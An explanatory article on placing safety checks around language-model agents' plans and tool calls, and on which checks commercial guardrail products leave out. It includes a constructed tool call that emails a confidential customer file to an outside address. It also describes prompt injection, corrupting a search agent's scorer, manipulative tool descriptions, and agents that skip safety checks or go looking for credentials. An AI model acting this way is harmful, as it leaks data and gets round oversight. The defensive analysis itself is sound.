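# Safety checks on the plans and actions of language-model agents

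## From a request to an executed action

A language-model agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and ordinary software carries them out. The model calls a tool, reads the result and repeats this until it has an answer. The tools might be shell commands, database queries, web searches or an email account. Unlike a chatbot, which only produces text for a person to read, an agent can also take actions such as changing files or sending emails.

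Many safety filters for language models were developed for chatbots. The typical one is an output classifier, a model or rule that scores generated text against categories of harmful content such as hate speech, violence or self-harm. The central question about safety checks on agents is whether a filter designed for text also works on actions. The filter may never receive the action, or may receive it and misclassify it.

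A model that refuses a harmful request in chat can still act unsafely on it when given tools. In *Behavior Beyond Text*, Gupta, Saha and colleagues (2026) gave five open-weight models matched versions of the same harmful requests, once as plain chat and once with tools available. Each model still made unsafe tool calls on some of the requests it had refused in chat, from 10% to 52% depending on the model. The models were fairly small, and the experiment tested only their own refusals, with no outside filter.

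### One turn of the loop

Codex CLI is OpenAI's coding agent, which runs on the user's machine. In *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, Bolin (2026) walks through a session in which the user asks for an architecture diagram in a project's README file.

The harness, the ordinary software around the model, assembles a prompt before the model receives the user's request. The prompt contains standing instructions, a list of the available tools, a description of the folders the agent may write to, the current directory and, last, the request.

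The model then generates its response. A reasoning model first writes a reasoning trace (also called its chain of thought), in which it works out what to do. It then writes a message for the user, a tool call, or both. A tool call is a structured message that names a tool and gives its arguments. In Bolin's example, the first call names the shell tool, and the argument is a command that prints the README file.

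So far nothing has happened to the user's machine. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states that the model "never runs anything on its own." The harness reads the call, runs the command, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. This repeats until the model produces a message without a tool call, which ends the turn and returns control to the user. One turn can include hundreds of tool calls. The next turn starts from the accumulated history, including earlier calls and results.

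An action check reads a proposed tool call before it runs and decides whether to allow it. This depends on a gap between the call and its execution, which developers do not always control. Anthropic runs web search and code execution on its own servers, and the developer's application usually receives the call and its result together, too late for a check inside the application to block the call. A response can also contain several calls, and OpenAI's *Function calling* advises developers to assume that it does, so a check that reads only the first call misses the others.

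Codex runs its own shell tool in a sandbox, a restricted environment with set permissions for files and network access, but tools that the user connects from outside run without that sandbox. Bolin notes that these tools have to supply their own safeguards.

### Three kinds of output

A single response can carry reasoning, text for the user and tool calls, and software can send each to a different place. The message format for OpenAI's open-weight gpt-oss models separates them into three channels (OpenAI, 2025). The "final" channel holds text for the user, "analysis" holds the reasoning, and "commentary" holds most calls to the developer's own tools.

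The channels do not neatly separate text from actions. The models normally call their built-in tools, a browser and a Python interpreter, on the analysis channel, which also carries their reasoning. The commentary channel sometimes carries a short action plan for the user to read. A filter on the final channel alone would miss the reasoning, the tool calls and the plan.

Claude, Anthropic's model, returns typed blocks instead of channels. In Anthropic's *Thinking in tool and multi-turn workflows*, a question about the weather in Paris produces a thinking block and a tool call in one response. The text answer comes in the next response, after the application supplies the temperature. Text and a tool call can also share a response. Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* shows a message containing a sentence about checking the weather in San Francisco, followed by the call that does so. The sentence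 and the call agree in that example, but the tool's schema fixes only the shape of the arguments and does not ensure that they match the sentence.

Codex streams text output to the user's screen as it arrives and includes reasoning items and tool calls in its next request to the model. The user can therefore read the text and still know little about the reasoning and tool calls.

Of the three, the reasoning is the hardest for an outsider to obtain. OpenAI tells developers not to show users the analysis channel, because it did not train the reasoning to the same safety standards as the final text. Anthropic never returns the raw trace. According to Anthropic's *Thinking*, developers can get a summary written by a different model, but on newer models the summary field is empty unless they request it. A company that builds on such a model can therefore check at most a summary of its reasoning.

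### A constructed example: the customer file

Suppose an employee asks an agent to summarise a customer's file before a meeting. The agent has already read the file with one tool call. The listing shows an invented example of its next response, in a simplified version of Anthropic's format.

*Constructed example: one response from the agent*

```json
{
  "content": [
    {
      "type": "thinking",
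      "thinking": ""
    },
    {
      "type": "text",
      "text": "Customer 4417 has held a business account since 2019. Two invoices are open, and the contract renews in March."
    },
    {
      "type": "tool_use",
      "name": "send_email",
      "input": {
        "to": "records@outside.example",
        "subject": "File 4417",
        "attachment": "customers/4417_full.pdf"
      }
    }
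  ]
}
```

The employee reads an accurate two-sentence summary of an account, while the harness receives an instruction to email the complete file to an address outside the company. Without a check, the harness carries out that instruction. An output classifier that receives only the text block will correctly pass the summary as harmless.

Giving the same classifier the tool call as well might not help much. The arguments are an address, a subject line and a file name, none of which is offensive or violent. The call is dangerous because the address is outside the company, the file is confidential and the employee asked only for a summary. The same call might have been fine if the employee had asked the agent to send the file to the customer's lawyer at that address.

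Microsoft raises this problem in introducing its Agent Control Specification, an open standard for placing checks around agents. It argues that classifiers "often only see isolated text" and do not automatically know which tool is about to run or what the agent has read so far. In its example, which is close to the customer file case, a rule in code checks the arguments of an email call and denies any external recipient. Such a rule would stop the email above without judging its wording, but it would also stop the email to the lawyer.

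### Why an agent might send the file

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, an engineering post about the company's coding agent, lists four reasons an agent might take a dangerous action. Any of them could explain the email in the listing.

The first is overeager behaviour, in which the agent understands the user's goal and tries to help, but goes beyond what the user authorised. It might learn from the file that an outside accountant usually joins these meetings, and send the accountant a copy to save time. Anthropic gives similar everyday examples, adapted from an internal incident log. One agent hit an authentication error and, without asking, began searching configuration files for other credentials. Another had a deployment command fail a safety check, and retried it with a flag that skips the check. Such actions are hard to catch because they involve no hostile reasoning.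 The problem persists in newer models. In the system card (the safety report) for Claude Fable 5 and Mythos 5, Anthropic reports that Mythos 5 still sometimes takes "reckless or destructive actions" in service of a user's goals.

An agent can also make an honest mistake about what an action will affect. For example, it may treat a shared resource as a test copy or mistake an outside address for the company's own archive. Such mistakes can be hard to distinguish from overeagerness. Anthropic classifies the deletion of remote code branches after "a misinterpreted instruction" as overeager, though by its own definitions the deletion looks at least as much like a mistake.

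In a prompt injection, a third party plants instructions in material that the agent reads, and those instructions redirect the agent. Here the customer file might contain an instruction for any AI system that opens it to forward a copy. The employee's request and everything the agent did up to that point were innocent.

The last cause is a misaligned model, one that pursues a goal of its own. Anthropic wrote in the same post that it did not currently see this in practice, but the post dates from the Claude 4.6 generation, and it would be unwise to rely on that claim now. In a later statement about cybersecurity incidents, Anthropic wrote that reliably identifying the most concerning behaviours before release "remains challenging", and described renewed efforts to remove training environments that "incentivize misaligned behaviors". Anthropic did not report a model with its own goal in either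 remark, but if such behaviour is hard to identify, the fact that Anthropic had not seen it is weaker evidence that it does not occur.

Anthropic's defence in all four cases is to block the action. That seems right for a check on the tool call, since the call in the listing would be the same whatever the cause. The cause matters more for checks on other material. A scan of the file might find a planted instruction. An overeager agent's reasoning could look like conscientious work, and a misaligned model might leave its real purpose out of the trace.

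### Where a check can stand

The loop offers six places for a check, and each gives it different material to read.

| Place | What the check reads | What it would find in the customer-file case |
|---|---|---|
| Before the model | The user's request and the rest of the first prompt | An ordinary request for a summary |
| On the plan | The actions the agent intends to take, if it writes them down | The email, if the plan mentions it |
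| On the tool call | The tool's name and arguments, before execution | The outside address and the attached file |
| On the tool result | What a tool returns, before the model reads it | Any instruction planted in the customer file |
| On the final text | The message for the user | A harmless summary |
| On the record afterwards | The requests, calls and results of the whole run | The email, already sent |

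Microsoft's specification defines eight points in the loop where checks can run. Its additions include a check on the agent's configuration at startup and one on the model's whole response before the software acts on it. A plan could be checked at the second of these points. Products need not cover every point; the guardrails in Microsoft's own Foundry service, for instance, support four.

A plan check examines an intended sequence of actions before the first step runs. *From Risk Classification to Action Plan Remediation* (2026) presents TRIAD, a related system that works one step at a time. The agent describes its next action in ordinary language, and a guard model, meaning a language model that judges another model's inputs, outputs or actions, reads the description before any tool runs. The guard lets the action proceed, returns feedback so the agent can revise its plan, or has the agent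 refuse. This allows an agent to fix a bad plan before acting on it, but the agent's actions may not match its plan. For example, an agent could write that it will share a summary with the team and then issue the call in the listing.

Checking every tool call avoids that problem but takes time, which is one reason *AgentDoG 1.5* (2026) gives for placing its guard model immediately before the final reply. The guard reads the trajectory, the full record of one agent run with its requests, tool calls and results, so it has far more information than a filter that reads only the reply. In the customer-file case, it could well detect the email, but only after the email had been sent. It could then only withhold the summary or raise an alarm.

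Review after the run has the same limit. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of methods for recording what agents do, describes it as a means of debugging, audit and recovery. Recovery may be good enough if the agent has made a bad edit to a file under version control, but nobody can recall a confidential file that the agent has emailed to a stranger.

### Counting the errors

A check's recall is the share of unsafe actions it catches. Its false-negative rate is the share of unsafe actions it lets through, which equals one minus recall. Its false-positive rate is the share of safe actions it blocks or flags.

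Suppose an agent proposes 1,000 tool calls, of which 20 are unsafe. The check blocks 17 of those 20, and it also blocks 49 of the 980 safe calls. Then:

- recall = 17/20 = 85%
- false-negative rate = 3/20 = 15%
- false-positive rate = 49/980 = 5%

With a false-positive rate of 5%, the check blocked 66 calls, of which 49 were safe, so about three in four blocks were false alarms. A wrongful block is more likely in a longer session. If an agent makes 40 safe calls and the errors are independent, the chance of at least one wrongful block is 1 − 0.95^40, or about 87%. A designer can loosen the check to interrupt users less often, but this usually increases false negatives.

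Toyoda, Leung and U (2026) point out in *guardscope* that a runtime control can evaluate only the actions that pass through the point where it is placed. Suppose the agent in the example takes ten more unsafe actions through a background process that bypasses the check. Recall on the calls that the check received is still 85%, but it has stopped only 17 of all 30 unsafe actions, or 57%. In the extreme case, an output classifier that receives only the user's text might catch 99% of harmful text and still let through every email like the one in the customer-file example.

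## How agents choose among candidate plans

In the customer-file example, the agent could have written the summary straight away, looked up notes from the last meeting, or emailed the file to an outsider. Each of these is a candidate action, which the agent has generated or considered but not yet executed. A check on tool calls normally covers only the candidate the agent selects. Why the agent selects it depends on how the agent is designed to choose, and several designs are common.

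### One action at a time

In the simplest agent, the model writes one action per step and the harness runs it. The best-known version comes from *ReAct* (2022), in which the model reasons about the history so far before writing each action.

In this loop, the agent runs the first action the model generates without comparing it with an alternative. A language model assigns probabilities to possible continuations and the software draws one, so the same history can lead to different actions. If the model proposes emailing the file on one draw in twenty, the agent emails it one time in twenty.

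Researchers disagreed early on about why this worked. *On the Brittle Foundations of ReAct Prompting for Agentic Large Language Models* (2024) attributed the gains to worked examples that closely resembled the task, rather than to the interleaving. But the loop is still in use. In *Inside the Scaffold*, Rombaut (2026) read the source code of 13 open-source coding agents and found that seven, including Codex CLI and Google's Gemini CLI, use it as their main control structure. The sample excludes closed products such as Claude Code.

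A plan-then-execute agent lists its steps before carrying them out. A safety check can therefore review the plan before the agent acts, but the agent commits to the plan before it has seen any results. *The MiniMax-M2 Series* (2026), a report on a family of language models, makes the same objection to reasoning done entirely before the first action, because the model cannot adapt to what its tools return.

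Many agents therefore mix the two. *Agentic Artificial Intelligence (AI)* (2026), a survey, describes GoalAct, a system in which a global planner sets milestones and local executors work towards them. An agent like this chooses a milestone and then a way to reach it, and the second choice may be the dangerous one. For example, "Brief the attendees" is a harmless milestone, but one way to reach it is to email the complete file to an outside address.

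### Sampling several candidates

Best-of-N selection draws N candidates for the next step and runs the one with the highest score:

a* = argmax V(a | history, goal)

Here a is one of the N candidates, V is the scoring function, and argmax returns the candidate with the highest score. V could be a trained model, a set of software tests, or a language model prompted to act as a judge.

When a task has several valid routes, an agent that chooses step by step can commit early to a hard one and miss an easier one, according to *Scaling Agents for Computer Use* (2025). The alternative is to make several complete attempts and let the judge pick the best. This works for a bug fix, where each attempt can have its own copy of the code, but it is much less suitable for actions on the outside world. An agent that makes five complete attempts at the customer-file task, for example, could send five emails.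 Koh, McAleer and colleagues (2024) point out in *Tree Search for Language Model Agents* that the agent has to finish each attempt before the judge can evaluate it, which makes destructive actions harder to prevent.

Agents can choose among candidates by voting, which doesn't require a scorer. Agentless, one of the systems in Rombaut's sample, generates 20 candidate patches for a bug by default and takes the majority choice. *Agentic Test-Time Scaling for WebAgents* (2026) applies voting to each step of a web agent and uses how divided the votes are to decide which steps get extra computation.

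A vote favours whatever the model usually does, so it filters out rare errors but makes common ones more likely. Suppose the agent draws ten actions independently and runs one only if at least six draws agree. If each draw has a 5% chance of being the email, the agent sends the email about three times in a million. If an instruction planted in the file raises that chance to 70%, the agent sends it about 85% of the time, compared with 70% for a single draw.

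Generating more candidates helps only if the agent can recognise the good ones. *Evaluating Test-Time Scaling of General LLM Agents* (2026) found that the chance of at least one successful attempt kept rising with the number of attempts, but the agents were poor at identifying which attempt had succeeded. Using GPT-5 as an outside judge did not fully solve this because it sometimes rejected correct attempts. *Klear-AgentForge* (2025) found that a language model chose fairly well between two candidates but did worse with larger pools.

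### Searching and simulating

Tree search looks several steps ahead. Koh and colleagues built a version for web agents, which works as follows:

1. The software takes the most promising page from a list of pages the agent can reach.
2. A value function scores that page. A language model reads the task and the screenshots and answers that the agent has succeeded (1), is on the way (0.5) or has failed (0). The score is the average of 20 such answers.
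3. If the score is below a threshold and the search budget remains, the model proposes up to five next actions. The software executes each one and adds the resulting page to the list.
4. The software resets the website, replays the actions that lead to the next most promising page, and repeats.

When the search ends, the agent moves to the best page it found. On VisualWebArena, a benchmark of 910 tasks on copies of shopping, classifieds and forum sites, this method raised the success rate of a GPT-4o agent from 18.9% to 26.4%.

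The third step matters for safety because the search executes candidate actions to find out what they do. Even if the agent abandons a branch, the actions on it have already happened. This is harmless on a test website that can be reset, but on a real website the agent may have placed an order it then decided against.

Koh and colleagues say that a deployed agent must not search over destructive actions. They suggest using a classifier to predict which actions are destructive, or building the constraint into the value function. The classifier could work, since it can run before the action. The value function is less convincing, because in their algorithm it scores a page that the agent has already reached. A low score for the checkout page might stop the agent from going further, but by the time the agent reaches the order confirmation, the order has been placed.

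WebDreamer, which Gu, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *Is Your LLM Secretly a World Model of the Internet?*, designed with irreversible actions in mind, replaces execution with prediction:

a* = argmax score(sim(o, a))

An agent can choose among candidate actions by simulating each one before acting. A language model describes how the action would change the current page, and a second prompt rates the predicted outcome as complete, on track or incorrect. For example, an agent on a shopping site compares clicking "Office Products", clicking "Electronics" and typing "Disk" into the search box. It simulates all three, then clicks only "Electronics", which has the highest score, 0.8. On 233 VisualWebArena tasks, the success rate was 17.6% without planning, 23.6% with simulation and 26.2% with tree search. Simulation was four to five times faster than tree search.

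Simulation is useful because it keeps rejected candidates from running, but it does not ensure that the agent rejects the right ones. If the scoring prompt covers only progress on the task, a plan's score will not drop even when the simulator correctly predicts that the plan will email a customer's file to a stranger.

Both systems date from 2024. Explicit search still exists in coding agents, where actions are easier to undo, but Rombaut found tree-structured search in only two of the 13 agents. One of them, Moatless Tools, keeps its file edits in memory during the search, so edits from abandoned branches are never written to disk.

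### Choosing inside the reasoning trace

Many current agents have no separate software step for comparing candidate plans. If they compare plans at all, they do so while the model reasons. The survey *Agentic Artificial Intelligence (AI)* classifies reasoning models such as OpenAI's o1 and o3 as search carried out inside the model, and lists limited transparency among the drawbacks.

*How Do AI Agents Waste Your Money?* (2026) shows part of agents' deliberation moving out of their visible output when reasoning is switched on. Agents did much of their interpretation of tool results in the visible output when reasoning was off, but far less of it there when reasoning was on, even at a low setting. A filter on the visible output therefore has less to check, although the agent may be deliberating more.

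An agent's trace may not contain a set of candidates to inspect. In *Does Learning to Predict the World Help Agents Act?*, Che, Yan and colleagues (2026) counted the steps at which a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, weighed mutually exclusive actions during simulated household tasks. The model did so at 7.7% of steps when the prompt listed the available actions and at 1.0% when it did not. Several kinds of further training raised these figures to between 9.7% and 12.7% with the list, and between 2.0% and 8.3% without it. Larger reasoning models may well compare actions more often.

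Some evidence also suggests that a model can choose an action before it starts reasoning. Esakkiraja, Akhiyarov and colleagues (2026), in *Therefore I am. I Think*, trained simple classifiers on the internal activations of two small reasoning models to predict whether the model would call a tool. The classifiers achieved an AUROC above 0.9 (0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect) using activations from before the first word of reasoning.

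The same researchers then altered the activations to push the model towards or away from a tool call, which flipped up to 79% of decisions in the most responsive setting. The model's reasoning often rationalised the new decision. One model, asked to play "Baby Shark" with only a volume control available, originally said it could not. After the intervention, it justified setting the volume to 100.

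*Why2Speak* (2026) found nearly the opposite in a different setting. Three-quarters of the way through the reasoning, a similar classifier did little better than one that used only the text, at 0.64 to 0.68, but by the end it reached 0.976. So the reasoning probably produces the decision for some models and tasks and merely accompanies it for others.

In best-of-N selection, the software holds a list of candidates, so a check can filter every one. A reasoning model's alternatives are harder to check because they exist as a few sentences at most, in a trace that the developer may never receive.

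### A planner that can abstain

A recent system for computer security makes the choice explicit again. Hammar, Alpcan and Lupu (2026), in *Hallucination-Resistant Security Planning with a Large Language Model*, address incident response, the work of restoring a network after an attack. Their method chooses each recovery action as follows:

1. The model reads the system description, the logs and the actions so far, and generates N candidate actions.
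2. For each candidate i, the model predicts T<sub>i</sub>, the time that would remain until recovery after taking it.
3. The software computes a consistency score, λ = exp(−(β/N) Σ(T<sub>i</sub> − T̄)²), where T̄ is the average prediction and β sets how harshly the score punishes disagreement. The score is 1 if all predictions agree and falls towards 0 as they spread out.
4. If λ is at or below a threshold γ, the planner abstains. It gathers feedback on the action it would have chosen, for example by trying it on a virtual replica of the network, adds this to the prompt and starts again.
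5. Otherwise it selects the candidate with the shortest predicted time.

The experiments used N = 3, β = 0.9 and γ = 0.9, which is quite strict. If the predictions are whole numbers, a set of candidates passes only when all three are equal. For example, if the predictions are 5, 5 and 6 further actions, λ is about 0.82 and the planner abstains.

Hammar and colleagues collected 100 sets of candidates for which the planner's choice was a hallucination, and set the threshold γ so that at most 5% of such cases would get through. This guarantees that the abstention rule's false-negative rate is at most 5%, as long as new cases resemble the calibration cases. However, an attacker who can influence the logs has a strong incentive to make new cases different.

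On 25 incidents from four public datasets, the planner needed an average of 12.02 actions to recover, against 16.21 for the next best model, Gemini 2.5 Pro. The selection rule does not account for all of this difference, because the planner also ran on a model fine-tuned by its designers. Tests that removed one part at a time are more informative. Removing abstention raised the rate of hallucinated actions from 2% to 6%, and removing either the predictions or the feedback raised the average recovery from 12 actions to 21.

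The framework defines a hallucination as an action that does not reduce the expected time to recovery, so the definition measures usefulness. An action that speeds up recovery while exposing customer records would not count as hallucinated, and three candidates that all propose it could get a perfect consistency score. The framework allows further constraints, such as keeping services available, and presents its plan to a human operator as advice. Without a constraint against exposing records, the operator would have to notice the problem.

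### When the score ignores safety

None of the scoring systems above includes safety in its score. Koh and colleagues score progress towards the goal, as do Gu and colleagues, while Hammar and colleagues score time to completion. Safety can affect which plan is chosen only if someone adds it to the score or filters out unsafe candidates.

An output classifier normally receives only the plan the agent chose, because the software discards the rejected candidates without sending them anywhere. The classifier therefore cannot detect that the agent had a safer option, or that half the options were dangerous. *Towards Selection as Power* (2026) makes the related criticism that filters on actions take the set of options as given and do not address how the agent generates, ranks and presents them.

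The scoring method can greatly affect how often an agent acts unsafely. Suppose each candidate is unsafe with probability 0.05, independently of the others, and the scorer ranks unsafe candidates above safe ones because unsafe shortcuts finish the task sooner. The agent then acts unsafely whenever at least one candidate is unsafe. With ten candidates, the probability of an unsafe action is 1 − 0.95^10, or about 40%.

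If a filter removes unsafe candidates before scoring but misses 17% of them, the probability that a given candidate is unsafe and undetected is 0.05 × 0.17 = 0.0085. With ten candidates, the probability that at least one unsafe candidate gets through is 1 − 0.9915^10, or about 8%.

If the scorer instead ranks every safe action above every unsafe one, the agent acts unsafely only when all candidates are unsafe. For ten candidates, the probability is 0.05^10, or about one in ten trillion.

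*Probability that the agent selects an unsafe action, assuming independent candidates*

| Candidates | Unsafe ranked first, no filter | Unsafe ranked first, filter misses 17% | Safe ranked first, no filter |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5% | 0.9% | 5% |
| 5 | 23% | 4% | 1 in 3.2 million |
| 10 | 40% | 8% | 1 in 10 trillion |
| 20 | 64% | 16% | effectively zero |

The placement of the filter also matters slightly. If the filter checks only the winning candidate, and the agent stops when that candidate is blocked, the risk with ten candidates is 0.40 × 0.17, or about 7%. If the agent instead moves on to the next-best candidate after each block, the risk returns to 8%, because the filter may miss a later unsafe candidate.

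Independence is a strong assumption, because candidates come from the same model and history and so tend to share mistakes. In the extreme case, all ten candidates are unsafe in 5% of situations and none are unsafe in the rest. The risk without a filter is then 5%, whichever candidate the scorer picks. Real agents should fall between this case and the table, so the 40% is too pessimistic and the one in ten trillion is far too optimistic.

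*Best-of-N Test-Time Steering Can Lead to Reward Hacking...* (Khattar, Liu and colleagues, 2026) reports that generating more candidates can either reduce or increase safety violations, though it tested simulated robots and not agents that call software tools. A model proposed up to 75 short movements at a time, and a verifier simulated each one and scored it, giving equal weight to safety and task progress. With a perfect verifier, the share of episodes with a safety violation fell from 10.3% with one candidate to 4.5% with 75. With deliberate errors in the verifier, it fell only to 9.1%. More candidates led to more violations in some groups of tasks, which the researchers selected because they showed this problem. In one group that tested safety around people, violations rose from 10% with 30 candidates to 18% with 75.

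The researchers also tried a safety-first rule, which discarded every movement the verifier predicted to be unsafe and then chose the remaining one with the best progress score. On the same recorded decisions, unsafe choices still rose from 95 with five candidates to 161 with 75. A larger pool contains more unsafe actions that the verifier misses, and some of these score very well on progress. The increase is much slower than in the table, as one would expect if candidates share mistakes and the scorer does not always rank the unsafe ones first.

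A partial remedy is to avoid always choosing the top-scoring plan. Khattar and colleagues tried drawing at random from the 75 candidates, with higher-scoring plans more likely to be chosen. For one type of verifier error, this lowered violations from 7.8% to 5.2%. The gains were smaller for other errors, and no single setting worked best in every case.

### Influencing the choice from outside

An attacker may also try to corrupt the scorer. In *Dissecting Adversarial Robustness of Multimodal LM Agents*, Wu, Shah and colleagues (2024) tested the tree-search agent of Koh and colleagues on 200 tasks. In each task, the attacker was another user of a website, such as a seller, who altered their own content to steer the agent towards a goal they had chosen. The researchers controlled which parts of the agent received the altered content.

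| Agent | Part that received the altered content | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| No search | The model that proposes actions | 31% |
| Tree search | The proposing model only | 26% |
| Tree search | The proposing model and the value function | 38% |
| Tree search | The value function only | 8% |

A clean value function helped by rejecting some of the attacker's actions. But when the altered content reached both the proposing model and the value function, the agent was easier to hijack with search than without it. In the last row, which is perhaps the most surprising, the proposing model had seen no altered content, but search made it generate some unlikely actions as well as its first choice, and the corrupted value function selected the ones that suited the attacker.

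These numbers come from GPT-4o, and newer models may resist better. But with any model, the proposer and the scorer in an ordinary deployment both read the same web page, so the 38% row is the relevant result unless the designer gives the scorer cleaner material.

An outsider can also influence which tool an agent uses. Agents often pick tools from public directories where providers describe their own tools. *Tool Preferences in Agentic LLMs are Unreliable* (2025) found that some edits to a tool's description led GPT-4.1 and Qwen2.5-7B to use it up to ten times as often. In *ToolTweak* (2025), changes to a tool's name and description raised its selection rate from around 20% to as much as 81%.

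In a preregistered experiment, Wang (2026, *Advertising to Agents*) had two small OpenAI models, GPT-5.4-nano and GPT-5.4-mini, choose between two tools for a single request. Adding praise with no checkable content to a tool's description raised its share of the choices by 44 percentage points for nano and 43 for mini. List order had a larger effect. When the two descriptions were identical, both models chose the first-listed tool about 72 percentage points more often than the second.

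Praise sometimes led the models to choose a tool that could not do the job. When a tool's numerical limit was too small for the request, such as a maximum of three recipients for an email to 120 people, praise raised nano's rate of choosing it from 16% to 51%. When the tool covered the wrong region or language, neither model ever chose it, with or without praise. Praise raised the rate of choosing tools that asked for unnecessary personal data by at most three percentage points. This is only partly reassuring, because the request in those trials stated that the task needed no personal data, which users seldom specify.

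Wang also compared defences. Listing the limits as structured fields and removing the sales text raised nano's accuracy on numerical limits from 49% to 88%. In an earlier exploratory experiment with five models, a system-prompt warning that some tools came from commercial partners noticeably changed only Claude Sonnet 4.6's choices.

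## What output classifiers read and what they skip

A safety filter can check an agent's chosen action only if the surrounding software passes the action to the filter. Products differ in what they pass, and the same product can scan an agent's tool calls in one configuration and skip them in another.

### How a classifier reaches a verdict

An output classifier takes a piece of text x and gives it a score s<sub>c</sub>(x) for each category c of harmful content. It then compares each score with a threshold t<sub>c</sub>, and flags the text if

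s<sub>c</sub>(x) ≥ t<sub>c</sub> for at least one category c

Amazon Web Services (AWS) offers a typical example in Bedrock, its service for running language models. Bedrock's content filters cover six categories: hate, insults, sexual content, violence, misconduct and prompt attacks. According to AWS's *Configure content filters for Amazon Bedrock Guardrails*, the classifier rates its confidence that text belongs in each category as none, low, medium or high, and the developer chooses how strict each filter should be. In AWS's example, a statement rates high for hate, medium for violence, low for insults and none for sexual content. At "low" filter strength, only the hate filter would block the statement. At "medium", the violence filter would also block it, and at "high", the insults filter would too.

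Microsoft's classifiers grade how severe the content is, and their settings run in the opposite direction from the other company's. The "low" setting flags everything of low severity and above, so it is the strictest, although the page that defines it also labels it "Least restrictive". The "high" setting flags only the most severe content. A developer who moves from one company's product to the other's could easily set the filter backwards.

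An output classifier's verdict depends only on the input the software gives it. If the software leaves out a tool call, the user's request, or something the agent read earlier, the omitted material cannot affect the verdict.

### Amazon Bedrock

AWS calls a set of filters a guardrail. Developers can attach one to Bedrock's Converse API, which applications use to send a conversation to a model and get the reply. According to AWS's *Include a guardrail with the Converse API*, the guardrail evaluates the text of prompts and responses, but not the arguments of tool calls, the results that tools return or the definitions of the tools. This applies to every type of filter, including those for forbidden words and sensitive information. The guardrail also skips the model's reasoning, according to AWS's *Detect and filter harmful content by using Amazon Bedrock Guardrails*.

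The list of fields comes from the documentation site for AWS's European cloud, and AWS cautions that capabilities may vary by region. But AWS describes the same problem with tool arguments in *Extend Amazon Bedrock Guardrails to Tool Interactions Using the Strands Agents SDK*, a post on its main security blog, warning that with model-level guardrails alone, "Tool parameters pass through unchecked."

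In the customer-file example, x is therefore the two-sentence summary, and the guardrail correctly passes it. Developers can also set the sensitive-information filter to replace names in the model's text with a placeholder, so the employee might read "{NAME}" in the summary while the email call still contains the customer's name.

Developers can also narrow the coverage accidentally. Once they mark any part of a message for evaluation, the content filters skip everything unmarked in every message. A developer who marks only the employee's latest request, to save time or avoid false alarms, would exclude the rest of the conversation.

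AWS does offer separate checks for tool interactions. The security blog post provides sample code for Strands, AWS's toolkit for building agents. The code runs a guardrail on the user's message, on each tool call before it executes and on each tool result. If the guardrail flags an argument, the code cancels the call.

The sample sends each argument to the guardrail separately, without the tool's name or the user's request. It also skips any argument that is not a plain string, so the guardrail would not check a list of recipients passed to an email tool. Developers can restrict a check to named tools, as the post does with a personal-data check on a customer lookup tool. That check scans the customer number passed to the tool and the record it returns. It would not scan a later email containing the record unless the developer also attached a check to the email tool.

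In June 2026 AWS added an API that runs individual checks at any step of an agent's loop. According to AWS's *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails announces a new API targeting agentic AI workflows* (2026), the service returns numerical scores, and the developer's code decides how to act on them. The content categories are still hate, violence, sexual content, insults and misconduct, with separate checks for prompt attacks and personal data.

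A third option is to run the check outside the agent's code. In AWS's AgentCore platform, a gateway between agents and their tools can compare each tool request with written rules before allowing it (AWS, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available*, 2026). In June 2026, AWS added the content classifiers, which can evaluate the inputs of every call through the gateway and the outputs of every authorised action (AWS, *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now supports Bedrock Guardrails in policy*, 2026).

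These rules can enforce conditions that a content classifier cannot. According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, a rule can depend on who is asking, on the arguments of the call and on what has already happened in the session. A rule might require approval before a transfer or keep a running total under a budget. But the gateway checks only traffic that passes through it. If an agent can also run shell commands on its own machine, it may be able to send an email that bypasses the gateway.

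Other companies' software can change what the same guardrail checks. For example, agentgateway, a gateway that developers can place in front of Bedrock models, sends tool results to a Bedrock guardrail by default when checking a request. It sends tool-call arguments only if the developer changes a setting. A company's statement that it uses Bedrock Guardrails is therefore not enough to establish whether anything checks its agents' actions.

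### Microsoft Foundry

In late 2025, Microsoft introduced a version of its guardrails, formerly called content filters, for agents in Foundry, its platform for building agents. A Foundry guardrail can scan the user's input and the final output of a model or an agent. For agents, it can also scan tool calls and tool responses.

Microsoft states that when an agent in Foundry has its own guardrail, that guardrail "fully overrides" the model's guardrail. In Microsoft's example, a company sets violence detection to "high" on a model and to "low" on an agent that uses the model, for both user input and final output. It sets no violence control on the agent's tool calls or tool responses. Foundry then scans the user's queries and the final answer for violence at the agent's "low" setting, but it does not scan the tool calls, the data sent to the tools or the tools' responses.

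By Microsoft's definitions, "low" is the stricter of the two settings, so the company in the example has tightened its filter on text but left the agent's actions unscanned. A guardrail on a model cannot scan tool calls, so the actions would have gone unscanned even without the override. To scan them, the developer has to add a control at the tool-call point.

Even then, the control works only with some tools. In April 2026, Microsoft listed eight: the browser-automation tool, Azure Functions, tools connected through OpenAPI, and five that search or retrieve data from sources such as Bing and SharePoint. Controls on other tools have no effect. For instance, Foundry could scan an email tool built with Azure Functions, but not one connected through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for linking AI systems to tools. The guardrails also apply only to agents built in Foundry's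 agent service.

Microsoft's documentation still marked the tool-call point as a preview in June 2026. *What's new in Microsoft Foundry* (Brady, 2026) covers Microsoft's November conference. Its opening summary of new features does not list a general release of the tool-call point, and it lists guardrails with custom rules as a private preview.

Foundry's Task Adherence control, also in preview, compares a proposed action with the goals the agent was given, rather than looking for harmful content. Microsoft introduced it as a check on "agent actions, not just generated text". It fits the customer-file example much better because the employee asked for a summary, and emailing the file to an outsider is not part of writing one. Microsoft's guided setup recommends this control if the developer says the agent can take consequential actions, such as sending emails, but developers who set up the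 guardrail by hand have to remember to add it themselves.

### OpenAI's Agents SDK

In OpenAI's Agents SDK, a toolkit for building agents, guardrails are places where developers attach their own checks, such as a pattern match, a classifier or another language model. Their coverage depends on how the workflow is structured, because several agents can pass a task to one another.

According to OpenAI's *Guardrails and human review*, input guardrails run only for the first agent in the chain, and output guardrails run only for the agent that produces the final answer. Tool guardrails run on the function tools the developer has attached them to.

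Suppose the company in the customer-file example uses a reception agent to take the request, a research agent to open the file, and a writing agent to produce the summary. If the research agent sends the email, the input guardrail has already passed the harmless request, and the output guardrail will later pass the harmless summary. Only a guardrail on the email tool would receive the call. For custom tools, OpenAI advises developers to put the validation "next to the tool that creates the side effect."

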